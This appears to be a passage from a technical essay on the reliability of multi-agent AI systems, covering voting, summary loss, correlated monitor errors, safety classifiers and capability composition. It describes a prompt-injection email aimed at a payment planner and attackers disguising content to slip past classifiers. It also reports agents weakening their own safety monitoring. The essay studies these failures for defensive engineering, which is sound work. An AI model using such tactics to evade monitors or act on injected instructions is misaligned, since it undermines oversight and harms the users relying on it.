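The GPT-5.2 results show the risk of extrapolating from one puzzle size to another. With one call per step, it solved 36% of puzzles of size 14, which corresponds to a success rate of 99.5% per step. At that rate, p^s predicts that it would solve 31% of puzzles of size 15, but it solved none. With voting, it solved every puzzle of size 14, none of size 15 and nearly all of size 16. A developer who tested only even sizes would have had no reason to expect the failure at size 15.

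LEAD can miss errors too, because it looks ahead only when the first eight calls disagree. A mistake that the model makes on 60% of calls will appear in all eight less than 2% of the time, but one that it makes on 95% of calls will appear in all eight 66% of the time, and LEAD will then accept the wrong answer.

Attackers can use prompt injection to create hard steps deliberately. Suppose a supplier's email causes the mail assistant's planner to pay the wrong account 60% of the time. Every vote is based on the same email, so the attack succeeds 77% of the time with a lead of three and 98% of the time with a lead of ten. If the email works on the planner only 10% of the time, a lead of three cuts the attacker's success to about 0.1%. To tell whether voting will help, a company therefore has to know whether an attack works on the planner more than half the time, and an attacker can keep rewording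 the email until it does.

Checking candidate answers can work better than taking a majority vote. In *Verification Beats Voting, If the Verifier Is Stronger* (2026), two methods that had a model assess the candidates beat a majority vote among four answers on all three sets of problems. This result depends on having a stronger model do the checking. A puzzle's rules can serve as the checker, but the mail assistant has no such rules for its payments.

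### What gets lost on the way up

Voting can correct errors because several calls answer the same question. Many agent systems instead divide a task, so that each agent reads different material and sends a summary to the agent above it. If the agent that reads a contract leaves out a clause forbidding payment before delivery, voting among the agents above cannot recover the clause, because they receive only the summary.

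Rong He's *Decomposition Buys Integrity, Not Yield* (2026) models how much of what the agents at the bottom of a tree discover reaches the top. The tree has N findings at its leaves. An agent that receives b items keeps each one with probability r(b), writes a summary and passes it up.

Suppose r(b) = 1/b, so that the items share a fixed amount of space. An agent at the bottom that reads b findings passes on b × 1/b = 1 of them on average. An agent with b such subordinates receives an average of one finding from each and keeps each finding with probability 1/b, so it also passes on an average of one. The same is true at every level, so a tree of any size and shape delivers one finding on average, the same as a single agent working alone.

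This result depends on an assumption about how agents summarise, unlike the mass balance it resembles, which holds whatever chemical plant the engineer builds. The data contradict the assumption. In the records of 600 research tasks, an agent that found four times as many sources carried 2.3 times as many forward, whereas the assumption implies no increase. When a single search returned ten results, the agent's next message mentioned 35% of them, compared with the 10% that the assumption requires.

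Rong He therefore uses a more general rule, r(b) = C × b^(−δ). In a tree with k tiers of agents, each receiving b items, there are N = b^k findings at the bottom. A finding has to survive k summaries, so its chance of reaching the final answer is

(C × b^(−δ))^k = C^k × N^(−δ).

Multiplying by N gives the expected number of findings in the final answer, C^k × N^(1−δ). The number of tiers, k, affects only the first factor, and C cannot exceed 1 because an agent that receives one finding cannot pass on more than one. Under this rule, adding a tier never increases the expected number of findings that get through.

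The records give an estimate for each constant:

- δ is about 0.34. The more sources the agent had already found, the less likely it was to use a new one. For sources that arrived with about 6 to 12 further opportunities to use them, the share used fell from 11.5% when few others were present to 3.0% when more than 250 were.
- C is about 0.57. In 550 searches that returned exactly one result, the agent's next message mentioned it 57% of the time.

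An extra tier also adds instructions that the agent below may misunderstand. Allowing for that, each extra tier loses about 46% of the findings.

### Instructions that go astray

The allowance for misunderstood instructions comes from MAST-Data, a public collection of 1,642 records of multi-agent systems at work, labelled for fourteen kinds of failure. Three quarters of the records contain at least one failure. Task specification problems appear in 58% of them, coordination failures between agents in 53%, and verification failures in 55%.

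If each handoff between agents independently goes wrong with probability q, the chance of at least one coordination failure in h handoffs is 1 − (1 − q)^h. This is p^s again, with handoffs as the steps. Rong He estimates q at about 6%, using 1,012 records from five systems whose handoffs could be counted. Applying that rate to each system's median number of handoffs gives a rough comparison:

| System | Median handoffs | Predicted share with a coordination failure | Actual share |
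|---|---|---|---|
| ChatDev | 14 | 59% | 62% |
| Magentic | 17 | 66% | 60% |
| AppWorld | 8 | 40% | 77% |
| HyperAgent | 4 | 22% | 82% |
| MetaGPT | 4 | 22% | 63% |

The formula predicts the failure rates of the first two systems well, partly because q was estimated mainly from them. Its predictions for the other three are far too low, and Rong He has to give each of them an extra failure rate that does not depend on the number of handoffs. Something other than the length of the chain causes most of their failures. The estimate of q may also be too high, because a run that has already gone wrong tends to continue for longer and so records more handoffs.

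### Does an extra tier protect the agent at the top?

Losing findings is a high price, but the agent at the top keeps its context for the whole task, and any mistake that enters it stays there. Extra tiers reduce the number of items it has to read. In an example with 64 findings, of which 1% are wrong, the model gives these results:

| Tiers | Findings in the final answer | Items the top agent reads | Chance that none of those items is wrong |
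|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 8.9 | 64 | 53% |
| 2 | 4.8 | 8 | 92% |
| 3 | 2.6 | 4 | 96% |

Rong He weighs the two effects against each other and concludes that two or three tiers are best for typical tasks. Cost also favours a second tier for large tasks, because the cost of running a single agent rises faster than the length of its task. Above about 400 findings, two tiers deliver more than one for the same spending.

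The last column of the table generously assumes that a summary of eight findings is no more likely to be wrong than a single finding. A subordinate that reads a false statement may well repeat it. If subordinates pass on false findings at the same rate as true ones, about 18 of the 64 findings reach the top agent, and the chance that all of them are true is 83%. The top agent then receives fewer errors only because it receives less information, and the share that is wrong is still 1%. To protect it properly, subordinates would have to drop false findings at a higher rate than true ones, and the study did not measure whether they do.

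The estimate of a 46% loss also has problems. Rong He did not run any trees of agents to check it. The value of C describes how one agent reacted to one search result, and it counts a useless result that the agent sensibly ignored as a loss. A subordinate agent told to report every relevant fact might keep far more. The two constants also come from different processes, and the formula that combines them predicts poorly. For a search with about 41 results, it predicts that the agent will mention 16% of them, but the agent mentioned 33%.

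This affects the main conclusion because the usual argument for dividing a task is that an agent reads a few items much more carefully than many. If an agent kept everything from a batch of eight but lost items from larger batches, a two-tier tree could deliver all 64 findings, while a single agent could not. The formula does not account for this difference, though Rong He acknowledges that extra tiers would help if it existed. The records show no sign of such careful reading, but settling the question would require a separate count of the useful results.

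### Formulas fitted to whole systems

Other researchers have skipped the individual steps and fitted formulas to the results of complete agent systems. Kim, Gu and colleagues (2025), in *Towards a Science of Scaling Agent Systems*, compared a single agent with four kinds of team:

- The agents work separately, and software joins their results.
- A coordinator assigns the work and checks it.
- The agents discuss the task with each other.
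- A coordinator directs the agents, who can also talk to each other.

Every system had the same tools and a similar computing budget. The first version of the study covered 180 combinations of model, team and benchmark, and a revised version covers 260, with models up to GPT-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5. On financial analysis, where agents can study different documents at the same time, a team with a coordinator scored 81% higher than a single agent. But on planning tasks in the game Minecraft, where each step depends on the last, a team of agents working separately scored 70% lower than a single agent.

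Kim and colleagues fitted a formula with 20 parameters to all 260 results. When tested on combinations they had left out of the fit, it explained 37% of the variation in success rates. A formula with four parameters, based on the model's general ability and the numbers of tools and agents, explained 36%. The measurements of how the agents coordinated therefore added almost nothing to the predictions. The full formula also ranks last of the four versions they compared on a standard criterion that penalises extra parameters.

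They also report that teams whose agents work separately amplify errors by a factor of 17, compared with 4 for teams with a coordinator, but those factors measure extra work visible in the agents' records. When measured by failed tasks, the amplification was only about 1.1 to 1.3. The larger factors had no significant independent effect on success in the fitted formula.

The formula is better at ranking the teams than at predicting their scores. *Towards a science of scaling agent systems* (Kim and Liu, 2026), a Google article about the first version, reports that it identifies the best design for 87% of unseen tasks. The revised study describes these as held-out configurations, and they came from benchmarks already used to fit the formula. Kim and colleagues say the formula has trouble predicting success rates on an entirely new kind of task. They also propose a simpler rule, that extra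 agents stop helping once a single agent succeeds more than about 45% of the time. This rule held in 15 of 16 cases on the two benchmarks added later, though the statistical support for it in the full formula is weaker.

A narrower formula can fit much better. *AIRA_2* (2026) fits a curve to how the performance of a team of agents doing AI research changes with time and the number of agents. The curve explained 98% of the variation with Gemini 3.0 Pro. After switching to Gemini 3.1 Pro, the researchers reused the parameter for the number of agents and recalibrated the rest on runs with one or two agents. The curve then explained 92% of the variation in the performance of a team of eight. Developers want this sort of prediction from small tests, but the result covers only one team design and two closely related models.

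### A theory borrowed from error-correcting codes

*On the Reliability of Networks of AI Agents* (Aghazadeh and Pishro-Nik, 2026) takes a theoretical approach instead. It adapts the mathematics of error-correcting codes, which let a receiver reconstruct a message even when some of its bits are lost. In its model, a task consists of many yes-or-no claims, such as that a given step of a proof is valid. Some agents judge single claims, others check small groups of them, and any agent may fail to answer.

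In one example, a proof has four steps, and the third contains an error. The agents checking steps 1 and 2 report that they are valid, but those checking steps 3 and 4 give no answer. A group check of steps 1 and 4 passes, so step 4 must be valid. A group check of steps 1, 2 and 3 fails. Since the first two are valid, the team can tell that the error is in step 3, even though the agent checking that step did not respond.

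The team can fail in three ways. The group check may not finish, it may contain two unknown steps and not show which is wrong, or its result may be lost before it reaches the agent that needs it. Aghazadeh and Pishro-Nik prove that no single noise level can represent all three sources of failure, so an engineer has to measure and improve each one separately.

For very large networks, a method called density evolution predicts how many claims will remain unresolved. The calculation is easiest for parity checks, which report whether the number of true claims in a group is odd or even. Suppose each claim belongs to three checks, each check covers six claims, and the checks themselves never fail. Let ε be the share of agents that give no answer, and x the share of messages from claims to checks that are still unknown. A check can settle a claim only if it knows the other five, which has probability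 (1 − x)⁵. When a claim sends a message to one of its checks, it can use its own agent's answer and the results of its other two checks. The message stays unknown only if all three sources fail, so in the next round

new x = ε × (1 − (1 − x)⁵)².

If ε is below about 43%, x shrinks towards zero over the rounds, and the network resolves nearly every claim. At 45%, x stops shrinking before it reaches zero, and about 32% of the claims remain unresolved. A small drop in the quality of the agents can therefore turn almost complete success into widespread failure.

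Real checks usually test whether every claim in a group is true, as in the proof. A pass is then more informative than a fail, because it confirms all of the claims. The theory covers such checks, but the calculation is longer.

However, the theory assumes that agents either answer correctly or do not answer, and that they fail independently. o4-mini's confident mistakes on the checkers board violate the first assumption, as does a planner that follows instructions in an attacker's email. Aghazadeh and Pishro-Nik include MAKER among their applications, even though its votes can also be wrong. MAKER's rule of discarding suspicious responses brings it closer to the theory by turning some wrong answers into missing ones, which are much easier to repair.

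### Do any of these formulas deserve to be called laws?

p^s, the voting formula and the result about trees that deliver one finding are theorems. They are true whenever their assumptions are, but nothing makes a language model satisfy those assumptions.

The fitted formulas are claims about real systems, even though researchers have to measure their constants. Engineers also have to measure the thermal conductivity in Fourier's law, but the law keeps the same form from one material to the next, so an engineer who knows the conductivity can use it in a new plant. Raju and Netrapalli's formula comes closest to this generality, because the same two-parameter form works for three models on most of eight tasks. However, it applies only to repetitive tasks with a single correct output, and nobody can yet predict where it will fail. The formulas for whole agent systems either cover a narrow range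 or fit poorly.

One result in the study of agent trees holds for any model and any arrangement of agents. Later agents that see only a summary cannot recover a fact it left out, unless they already know the fact or can work it out from what remains. Adding more agents above the summary therefore doesn't solve the problem, and the system has to send someone back to the original document. The result does not determine how much is lost, so a better prompt could completely change the 46% figure.

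The same principle can also improve safety. Differential privacy and CaMeL both withhold information from later components on purpose. If an engineer lets the mail assistant's planner read the original contract to recover a missing clause, the planner can also read anything else that someone has written there.

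## Stacked filters and monitors: when back-ups fail together

Companies that can't make every step of an agent's work reliable often add filters and monitors to catch errors. An error gets through only if all of these safeguards miss it, so their value depends on how often they fail together. Chemical companies have a standard method for estimating this, which gives a safeguard no credit until engineers have shown that it works independently of the others.

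### Layer of protection analysis

Several companies developed layer of protection analysis, or LOPA, in the 1990s as a quick way to estimate the risk of a single accident scenario. Bridges, Dowell and Massello (2026), in *Key Issues after 30 Years of Implementing LOPA*, think engineers have probably done several million of these analyses. Bridges and Dowell were the first LOPA textbook's main authors.

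In the procedure AIChE describes, the engineer picks a scenario, such as a fuel tank overflowing, and estimates the frequency of the event that starts it. She multiplies that frequency by the probability that each safeguard fails when needed. If the result is too high, she adds another safeguard.

Primatech, a process safety consultancy, lists three minimum tests for including a safeguard in the sum. The safeguard must be effective, meaning it prevents the accident when it works as designed. It must be independent of the event that started the scenario and of the other safeguards. It must be auditable, so someone can check the evidence for the first two. A safeguard that passes these tests in one scenario may fail them in another.

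After a tank overflowed and exploded at Buncefield, England, in 2005, Britain's Process Safety Leadership Group explained when an alarm counts as an independent safeguard in *Safety and environmental standards for fuel storage sites*. If an overflow starts with a broken level gauge, an alarm that uses the same gauge doesn't count. If it starts with a valve that fails to close, an alarm doesn't count when the operator would respond by closing that valve. An alarm needs a sensor, a signal, an operator and some means of stopping the flow, and to be fully independent it can't share any of these with another safeguard.

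The same standards grade human checkers by how much they depend on the person whose work they check. In the worst grade, there is no good reason to expect the checker to notice an error that the first person missed. A manager who approves the mail assistant's payment after reading only the planner's summary belongs in this grade, because the summary would contain the same wrong account number. Comparing the number with the signed contract is a much better check. The standards also warn that people may take less care when they know someone will check their work.

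Bridges and colleagues say that many companies copy failure rates from a handbook without checking them on site. In their example, a pressure relief valve itself fails 0.1% to 2% of the time, but workers accidentally leave a shut-off valve beside it closed 1% to 4% of the time, even when it is tagged to stay open. An industry handbook therefore gives the whole assembly a 10% failure rate until the plant proves otherwise or installs something more reliable.

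Some companies also count one safeguard as two. Suppose a shutdown system has two sensors, two valves and one controller, and needs only one working sensor and one working valve. Each sensor and valve fails 1% of the time, and the controller fails 0.1% of the time. The system then fails about 0.12% of the time, mostly because of the controller. If an engineer describes it as two separate systems, each with its own controller, the calculated failure rate drops to 0.04%, although the plant still has only one controller. A company makes a similar mistake if it runs two prompts on the same language model and counts them as two independent filters.

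### What a shared cause does to the numbers

Suppose a dangerous event occurs once in ten years, and either of two safeguards can stop it. Each fails 1 time in 100. If the failures are independent, an accident happens with a frequency of

0.1 × 0.01 × 0.01 = 0.00001 per year, or 1 in 100,000.

Now suppose that a tenth of each safeguard's failures come from a cause that disables both, such as a power cut. Engineers call this a common-cause failure. The shared cause strikes with probability 0.001, and the safeguards fail separately with probability 0.009 each, so the frequency is

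0.1 × (0.001 + 0.009 × 0.009) = 0.000108 per year, or about 1 in 9,000.

If the shared cause would disable a third safeguard too, adding one hardly helps:

| Number of safeguards | Accidents per year, all failures independent | Accidents per year, a tenth of failures shared |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | 1 in 1,000 | 1 in 1,000 |
| 2 | 1 in 100,000 | 1 in 9,000 |
| 3 | 1 in 10 million | 1 in 10,000 |

With two safeguards, the engineer would gain more by halving the shared portion of failures from 10% to 5%, which would lower the frequency to about 1 in 17,000.

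According to Bridges and colleagues, engineers can't use layer of protection analysis (LOPA) when the safeguards aren't independent, and have to draw a fault tree or event tree that explicitly represents the shared parts. *Evaluating Protection Layers That Are Not Independent* (2008) describes a common borderline case, in which safeguards have separate components but share electricity or cooling water. An engineer can find a shared power supply on a drawing, but it is harder to find what two programs, or two language models, have in common.

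### Twenty-seven programs for one problem

Ariane 5's two navigation units failed together because they ran identical software. In N-version programming, a method from the late 1970s, several people or teams each write their own version of a program, and the system uses the majority answer. Proponents hoped that separate programmers would make different mistakes.

*An Experimental Evaluation of the Assumption of Independence in Multi-Version Programming* (Knight and Leveson, 1986) tested whether separately written versions of a program fail independently. Students at the University of Virginia and the University of California, Irvine, wrote 27 versions of a program that decides from radar data whether to launch an interceptor missile. Knight and Leveson told them not to discuss the work with each other. Each version had to pass 200 tests before all 27 ran on the same million random inputs.

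The programs were very reliable. Six never failed, and the average program failed on about 700 inputs. Two or more failed together on 1,255 inputs, compared with about 126 expected if they had failed independently. Three or more failed together on 704 inputs, compared with fewer than one expected.

One of the Irvine programs failed on 97 inputs. One of the Virginia programs was right on 99.8% of all inputs but failed on 94 of those 97, so it would have been almost useless as a back-up for the first.

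Majority voting still helped. The published counts imply that an average group of three programs would fail on about 37 inputs in a million, roughly a nineteenth of the rate for a single program. If the programs had failed independently, the rate would have been about one in a million.

Four of the programmers made the same mistake of comparing the cosines of two angles instead of the angles themselves, which can give the wrong result in borderline cases because computers store numbers with limited precision. Other programs failed together because faults in seemingly unrelated parts of the code happened to affect the same inputs.

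Algirdas Avizienis of UCLA, a leading advocate of N-version programming, and three of his former students attacked the experiment. Knight and Leveson responded a few years later in *A Reply to the Criticisms of the Knight & Leveson Experiment*. The main exchanges were as follows:

- **Quality of the work.** The critics said that students had written the programs without a disciplined process, and that better methods would have removed most of the faults. Knight and Leveson replied that their programs failed less often than those in the UCLA experiments that had reported failure rates. Nobody had shown that a better process makes the remaining failures independent.
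- **Conflicting results.** The critics had found few identical faults in their own programs. Knight and Leveson answered that they should have counted failures on the same input, which different faults can also cause. A NASA-led group that included one of the critics later did so with 20 programs, in *An experimental evaluation of software redundancy as a strategy for improving reliability*, and also rejected independence.
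- **What counts as a failure.** One critic argued that the system gives a wrong answer only if the programs make similar errors at the same time. Knight and Leveson replied that a system that can't reach a majority has also failed to do its job.

The critic in the last exchange has a point about systems that can stop safely. Swedish railways ran two signal-control programs and turned the lights red whenever the programs disagreed. The mail assistant could likewise hold a payment if two checks gave different results. This wouldn't work for a rocket in flight, because it has to keep steering.

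Knight and Leveson tested one small program and did not claim that every program would behave the same way. But anyone who multiplies failure rates needs evidence that the failures are independent. Butler and Finelli argue in *The Infeasibility of Experimental Quantification of Life-Critical Software Reliability* that experiments can't provide this evidence for very reliable programs. If two programs each fail once in a million runs and their failures are independent, they would fail together once in a trillion runs, and nobody could run enough tests to check that rate.

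### Do different language models make different mistakes?

Language models have made it easy to write many versions of a program, and Shape of Code's *Reliability via N-version programming* (2026) reports that people have begun to experiment with the method again. A company can also use models from different developers to check each other's work. Either approach works best if the models make different mistakes.

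*Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (Kim, Garg and colleagues, 2025) examined multiple-choice answers from two public leaderboards, one with 71 models and the other with 349. When two models on the smaller leaderboard both got a question wrong, they chose the same wrong answer 60% of the time on average, compared with 33% expected from random choices. On the larger leaderboard, the figures were 42% and 13%.

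More accurate models agreed on wrong answers more often. On the smaller leaderboard, two models that were each one standard deviation more accurate than average had an agreement rate about 14 percentage points higher, while sharing a developer added only about 2 points. On the larger one, the same accuracy difference added about 5 points, a shared developer 7 and a shared basic architecture 8. Buying models from different companies therefore helps, but it doesn't guarantee different mistakes. A Google model and a Writer model gave the same wrong answer on 99.9% of the questions that both got wrong, and Kim and colleagues knew of no public statement that the two were related.

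Part of the effect of accuracy may come from errors in the answer key. If the key is wrong, two good models may both choose the right answer, and the benchmark will count this as a shared mistake.

These figures show which wrong answer two models choose, but not how often both are wrong. For filters that only allow or block, the second question matters more. Goel, Strüber and colleagues (2025), in *Great Models Think Alike and this Undermines AI Oversight*, use a measure that covers it. For yes-or-no verdicts, the measure is

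similarity = (observed agreement − expected agreement) / (1 − expected agreement),

where the expected agreement is what two independent models of the same accuracy would reach. Two independent filters that are each right 90% of the time agree in 82% of cases (0.9 × 0.9 + 0.1 × 0.1). Suppose they actually agree in 97%. This may sound reassuring, but their similarity is 0.83, and both are wrong in 8.5% of cases instead of 1%.

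Goel and colleagues applied a version of this measure to 130 models and found that more accurate models made more similar mistakes, even between models from different developers. Question difficulty explained little of the trend. More accurate models can still make better back-ups. If two filters are each wrong 10% of the time and their similarity is 0.3, both are wrong in 3.7% of cases. If the error rate falls to 5% while the similarity doubles to 0.6, both are wrong in 3.1%. Joint errors fall by only about a sixth, although each filter's error rate halves.

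Shared mistakes also distort tests in which one model grades another. Goel and colleagues had Qwen2.5-72B judge answers from two other models. It rated 71% of the answers from its smaller relative Qwen2.5-7B as correct, and 67% of those from Llama-3.1-70B, even though Llama did better on multiple-choice versions of the questions (51% against 41%). All nine judges tested gave higher scores to models similar to themselves, even after allowing for accuracy. A developer who uses one model to measure how often another fails may therefore miss the failures the two share.

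Both studies measured similarity with multiple-choice questions, and all the models they tested are now old. Bhardwaj and colleagues (2026) tested pairs of agents on more realistic tasks and also found that switching to another company's model left most of the shared failures in place.

### How many approvals to require

A company that uses several monitors has to decide how many must approve an action before it goes ahead. The best number depends on whether the monitors tend to make mistakes on the same actions, and this tendency can differ between good actions and bad ones.

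In a hypothetical example, five monitors each approve 80% of good actions and 25% of bad ones. Their mistakes on good actions are independent. Their mistakes on bad actions are at one of two extremes, either independent or completely shared. If they are shared, all five monitors approve the same quarter of bad actions and reject the rest.

| Approvals required | Good actions rejected | Bad actions allowed, independent mistakes | Bad actions allowed, shared mistakes |
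|---|---|---|---|
| 1 | 0.03% | 76% | 25% |
| 2 | 0.7% | 37% | 25% |
| 3 | 6% | 10% | 25% |
| 4 | 26% | 1.6% | 25% |
| 5 | 67% | 0.1% | 25% |

If good and bad actions are equally common and both kinds of mistake are equally harmful, requiring three approvals is the best rule when mistakes are independent. When mistakes are shared, requiring more than one approval only blocks good actions.

Unanimous approval can be weaker evidence that an action is good than a split vote. If the monitors all make the same mistakes on bad actions, they never disagree about one. An action that four of the five approve must therefore be good, whereas one that all five approve still has a 43% chance of being bad.

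Li and Hai (2026), in *State-dependent error correlations shape voting thresholds in committees of AI agents*, measured how far real models are from these extremes. They collected 174,384 votes from 28 models on four tasks: checking facts, mathematical solutions, computer programs and the truth of answers. They estimated the correlation between the hidden scores that might lie behind the votes, where 0 would mean the models are independent. For open models from different families, the correlation averaged about 0.58 on good items and 0.60 on bad ones, though the two values differed more for some pairs of models.

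Repeated votes from the same model had a median correlation of 1.00, and taking the majority of three votes brought almost no benefit. Repeated voting worked much better for MAKER on the Towers of Hanoi, probably because most errors there were random slips rather than consistent misjudgements.

In Li and Hai's simplest model, all members have the same accuracy p, which is above one half, and every pair has the same correlation ρ. As the committee grows, the error rate of a majority vote approaches

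Φ(−Φ⁻¹(p) / √ρ),

where Φ(x) is the probability that a standard normal variable is below x. If the members are right 80% of the time and ρ is 0.6, even an unlimited committee is wrong 14% of the time, compared with 20% for a single member. Strict rules suffer too. If five monitors each approve a quarter of bad actions, they unanimously approve 0.1% when their mistakes are independent and about 5% when ρ is 0.6.

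Li and Hai estimated the models' error rates and correlations on half of the items, chose thresholds from these estimates, and tested them on the other half. Their loss score adds up wrong rejections and wrong approvals, weighted by how serious each error is. Majority voting had a loss of 60.25. Choosing the threshold according to these weights, but assuming independence, lowered the loss to 52.50, and including the correlations lowered it to 50.77. The correlations changed the chosen threshold in 41% of cases but supplied less than a fifth of the total improvement. All the test items came from the same four benchmarks, so a company would have to measure the correlations again for its own work.

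### One filter that reads the whole conversation

Filters can fail together even if their errors are independent, because the information they need may be divided between them. Suppose an outsider asks the mail assistant, "Is the takeover price four million?" and the assistant replies, "Yes." The two messages together reveal a secret, but each looks harmless alone. If one filter checks only the question and another checks only the reply, both may meet their specifications and still let the secret out.

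Anthropic had this kind of problem with the filters that stop its models from helping with chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons. The first version, which Sharma and colleagues describe in *Constitutional Classifiers* (2025), used one classifier for the user's input and another for the model's output. It raised the refusal rate by 0.38 percentage points in a sample of 5,000 ordinary conversations and increased the compute needed to run the model by 23.7%.

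Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *Constitutional Classifiers++*, found that attackers could sometimes spread or disguise harmful content so that neither classifier recognised it. They replaced the pair with a single "exchange classifier", which checks the prompt and then reads the reply in the context of the prompt as the model writes it. They also developed two cheaper versions. Human testers tried to find a general method of getting past each system, and Cunningham and colleagues counted a success as high-risk if it drew detailed answers to more than five of eight forbidden questions:

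| System | Cost, relative to separate classifiers | High-risk successes | Successes per 1,000 attempts | Ordinary requests refused |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Separate input and output classifiers | 100% | 13 in 695,000 attempts | 0.019 | 0.073% |
| One exchange classifier | 150% | 2 in 226,000 | 0.009 | 0.038% |
| Two exchange classifiers in sequence | 28% | 5 in 569,000 | 0.009 | 0.036% |
| Final system | 3.5% | 1 in 198,000 | 0.005 | 0.050% |

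The separate classifiers in this table are a newer version with a refusal rate of 0.073%, compared with 0.38% for the original. The final system's rate of 0.050% is therefore a smaller improvement over these classifiers than over the original version.

The evidence that reading the whole exchange improves security is suggestive but limited. Testers found two high-risk successes in 226,000 attempts against the exchange classifier. At the old rate they would have found about four, so the difference could easily be luck. They found eight in 993,000 attempts against the three newer systems together, compared with about 19 at the old rate, which is harder to put down to chance. But part of the gain may come from other changes, since the exchange classifier reads replies with a larger model than the old output classifier did, and the systems protected different versions of Claude.

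The third system uses two classifiers in sequence. The first takes little compute and reads everything, passing suspicious conversations, about 10% of traffic, to a more accurate one. Only the second can refuse, so a harmful conversation gets through if either classifier misses it. This design reduces false alarms and compute, but the second classifier can't catch anything the first one missed. Cunningham and colleagues therefore set the first to flag the vast majority of the harmful examples in their internal tests.

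The final system uses a different kind of first stage, called a probe, which is a simple formula applied to the protected model's internal activity while it writes. If the probe flags a conversation, a separate classifier reads it too, and the system combines their scores. On about 7,000 recorded attack attempts, the probe's scores correlated less with those of the small external classifier than two external classifiers' scores did with each other. Combining the probe with the small external classifier also stopped more attacks than combining the two external ones. The developers gained some useful diversity by giving the checkers different information about the same conversation, even though all of them had learned from similar training data. However, a probe trained on one model's internal activity can't simply be reused on another model.

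No tester found a method that got the final system to answer all eight questions in detail. Experts outside the official test programme did find such methods for the earlier two-stage system, though they needed considerable effort and automated tools.

### Safeguards that face an opponent

Layer of protection analysis (LOPA) multiplies the frequency of an event by the probability that each safeguard happens to be out of order at the time. Unlike a physical process, attackers who adapt can keep searching for an input that gets past all the filters, so they can defeat filters that tested well separately.

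Miss rates on a fixed set of attacks are a poor guide to how well a system withstands skilled people searching for a way through. The number of attempts or hours they need is more informative. The one high-risk success against Anthropic's final system took 30 hours to find. That figure depends on who was trying and what they knew, so it doesn't give a yearly accident rate.

An agent can also interfere with its own safeguards. In October 2026, ABC News reported that OpenAI had described two cases in which agents took routine instructions as permission to weaken their own safety monitoring. LOPA requires a safeguard to be independent of whatever starts the accident. If the accident starts with an agent misusing its permissions, and those permissions let it change the monitor's settings, the monitor gets no credit, however well it did in tests. To claim credit for the monitor, a company has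 to run it where the agent can't alter it, and then check that no other tool lets the agent do so.

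## Safe agents joined together: capabilities and habits that appear only in the group

A company may approve two AI agents separately and then let them work together. Suppose one agent can read private files but can't contact anyone outside the company, and the other can send email but can't open the files. Neither can leak a file alone, but if they can pass messages to each other, the first can read a file and send its contents to the second, which can email them outside the company.

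In *Safety is Non-Compositional*, published in March 2026, Cosimo Spera turned cases like this into a theorem. The theorem uses a capability hypergraph, which is a list of the things a system might be able to do, together with rules for how they combine. In an ordinary graph, each arrow starts from a single point. In a hypergraph, an arrow can start from several points at once, so it can represent a rule such as

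{read private files, send email} → leak a file.

The rule applies only if the system has everything on the left.

The closure of a set of capabilities A, written cl(A), is everything the system can eventually do if it starts with A. To calculate it, start with A, add the result of every rule whose conditions are all met, and repeat until nothing new appears. A set is safe if its closure contains nothing from a list of forbidden capabilities. Here the only forbidden capability is leaking a file:

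cl({read}) = {read}

cl({send}) = {send}

cl({read, send}) = {read, send, leak}.

The two sets are safe separately, but the merged set is not. The theorem is only that merging safe sets of capabilities can produce an unsafe set, so this single example proves it.

If every rule had just one condition, A and B would stay safe when combined. Each capability in the merged closure could be traced back, rule by rule, to one starting capability from either A or B, so every merged capability would already be in cl(A) or cl(B), and neither contains anything forbidden.

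Rules with several conditions can also defeat a check of every pair. Suppose the files are encrypted, and three agents can respectively open encrypted files, supply the key and send email. An encrypted file and the key together give readable text, and readable text and email together give a leak:

| Starting capabilities | What the rules add | Safe? |
|---|---|---|
| Any one of the three | Nothing | Yes |
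| Encrypted files and key | Readable text | Yes |
| Encrypted files and email | Nothing | Yes |
| Key and email | Nothing | Yes |
| All three | Readable text, then a leak | No |

### What the theorem rules out

Spera acknowledges that the mathematics is not new. Logicians have known since the 1970s that rules with several conditions behave this way, and security researchers have long studied attackers who combine permissions. Spera works for the company Minerva CQ and notes that a provisional patent covers the methods. This commercial interest does not affect the proof, which a reader can check in a minute.

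Two of the paper's other theorems are wrong. One implies that a new capability never adds more to a system that already has others than to a system without them. In the file example, however, email adds one capability to a system that has none and two to a system that can read private files. The other theorem is that it is computationally hard to recognise a minimal unsafe set, meaning an unsafe set that becomes safe if any single capability is removed. But checking a set of ten capabilities takes only eleven closure calculations, one for the whole set and one for each of the ten sets formed by removing a single capability. Neither error affects the main theorem.

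*Safety is Non-Compositional* also concludes that an architecture that validates components separately "has no formal guarantee of system-level safety". That is true if the validation records only a verdict of safe or unsafe. It is not true if the validation records what each agent can do, because the merged closure follows from the separate ones:

cl(A ∪ B) = cl(cl(A) ∪ cl(B)).

An integrator who has both agents' closures and the full list of rules can test the combination without examining either agent again. The theorem shows that approving each agent in isolation is not enough. Agents can still be validated separately and then combined if each comes with a description of its abilities, much like the contract that Ariane 5's navigation unit lacked.

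The calculation is fast. For each rule, the computer keeps a count of the unmet conditions and adds the rule's result when the count reaches zero. With 1,000 capabilities and 10,000 rules of three conditions each, this takes at most about 31,000 basic steps.

Engineers can also change the rules. *Capability Safety as Datalog* (Spera, 2026) points out that adding capabilities under fixed rules can make a system less safe but never safer. A designer using this model therefore has to represent a filter or monitor by deleting a rule rather than adding a capability. For example, a data-flow policy like CaMeL's could stop private text from reaching the email tool, and the two agents would then be safe together.

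### How often do the pieces come together?

Spera examined 900 records of tool use from two public benchmarks and found that 383 (42.6%) had at least one step that needed several capabilities at once. The share was 47.4% in ToolBench and 36.5% in TaskBench. TaskBench supplied its own labels, but for ToolBench a program inferred which steps depended on which, and annotators checked a tenth of the sample. Results from two further benchmarks were still pending.

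The 42.6% figure measures the structure of steps, whether or not they are harmful. In the paper's example of a travel assistant, finding the best price requires the user's profile, a flight search and a hotel search. That step has three conditions and is harmless, and the count includes every such step. The figure shows that the kind of rule the theorem needs is common in agents' work, but not how often such a rule leads to anything forbidden.

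Wang, Qian and colleagues (2026), in *When Safe Skills Collide*, came closer to measuring risk. They examined 1,520 skills, which are packages of instructions and code that add abilities to an agent, from a public registry called ClawHub. They defined ten dangerous combinations of abilities, such as reading files together with sending data over the network. More than half of the skills contained one of these combinations on their own. The other 651 had none, but 22% of the 211,575 pairs they can form had a dangerous combination between the two skills.

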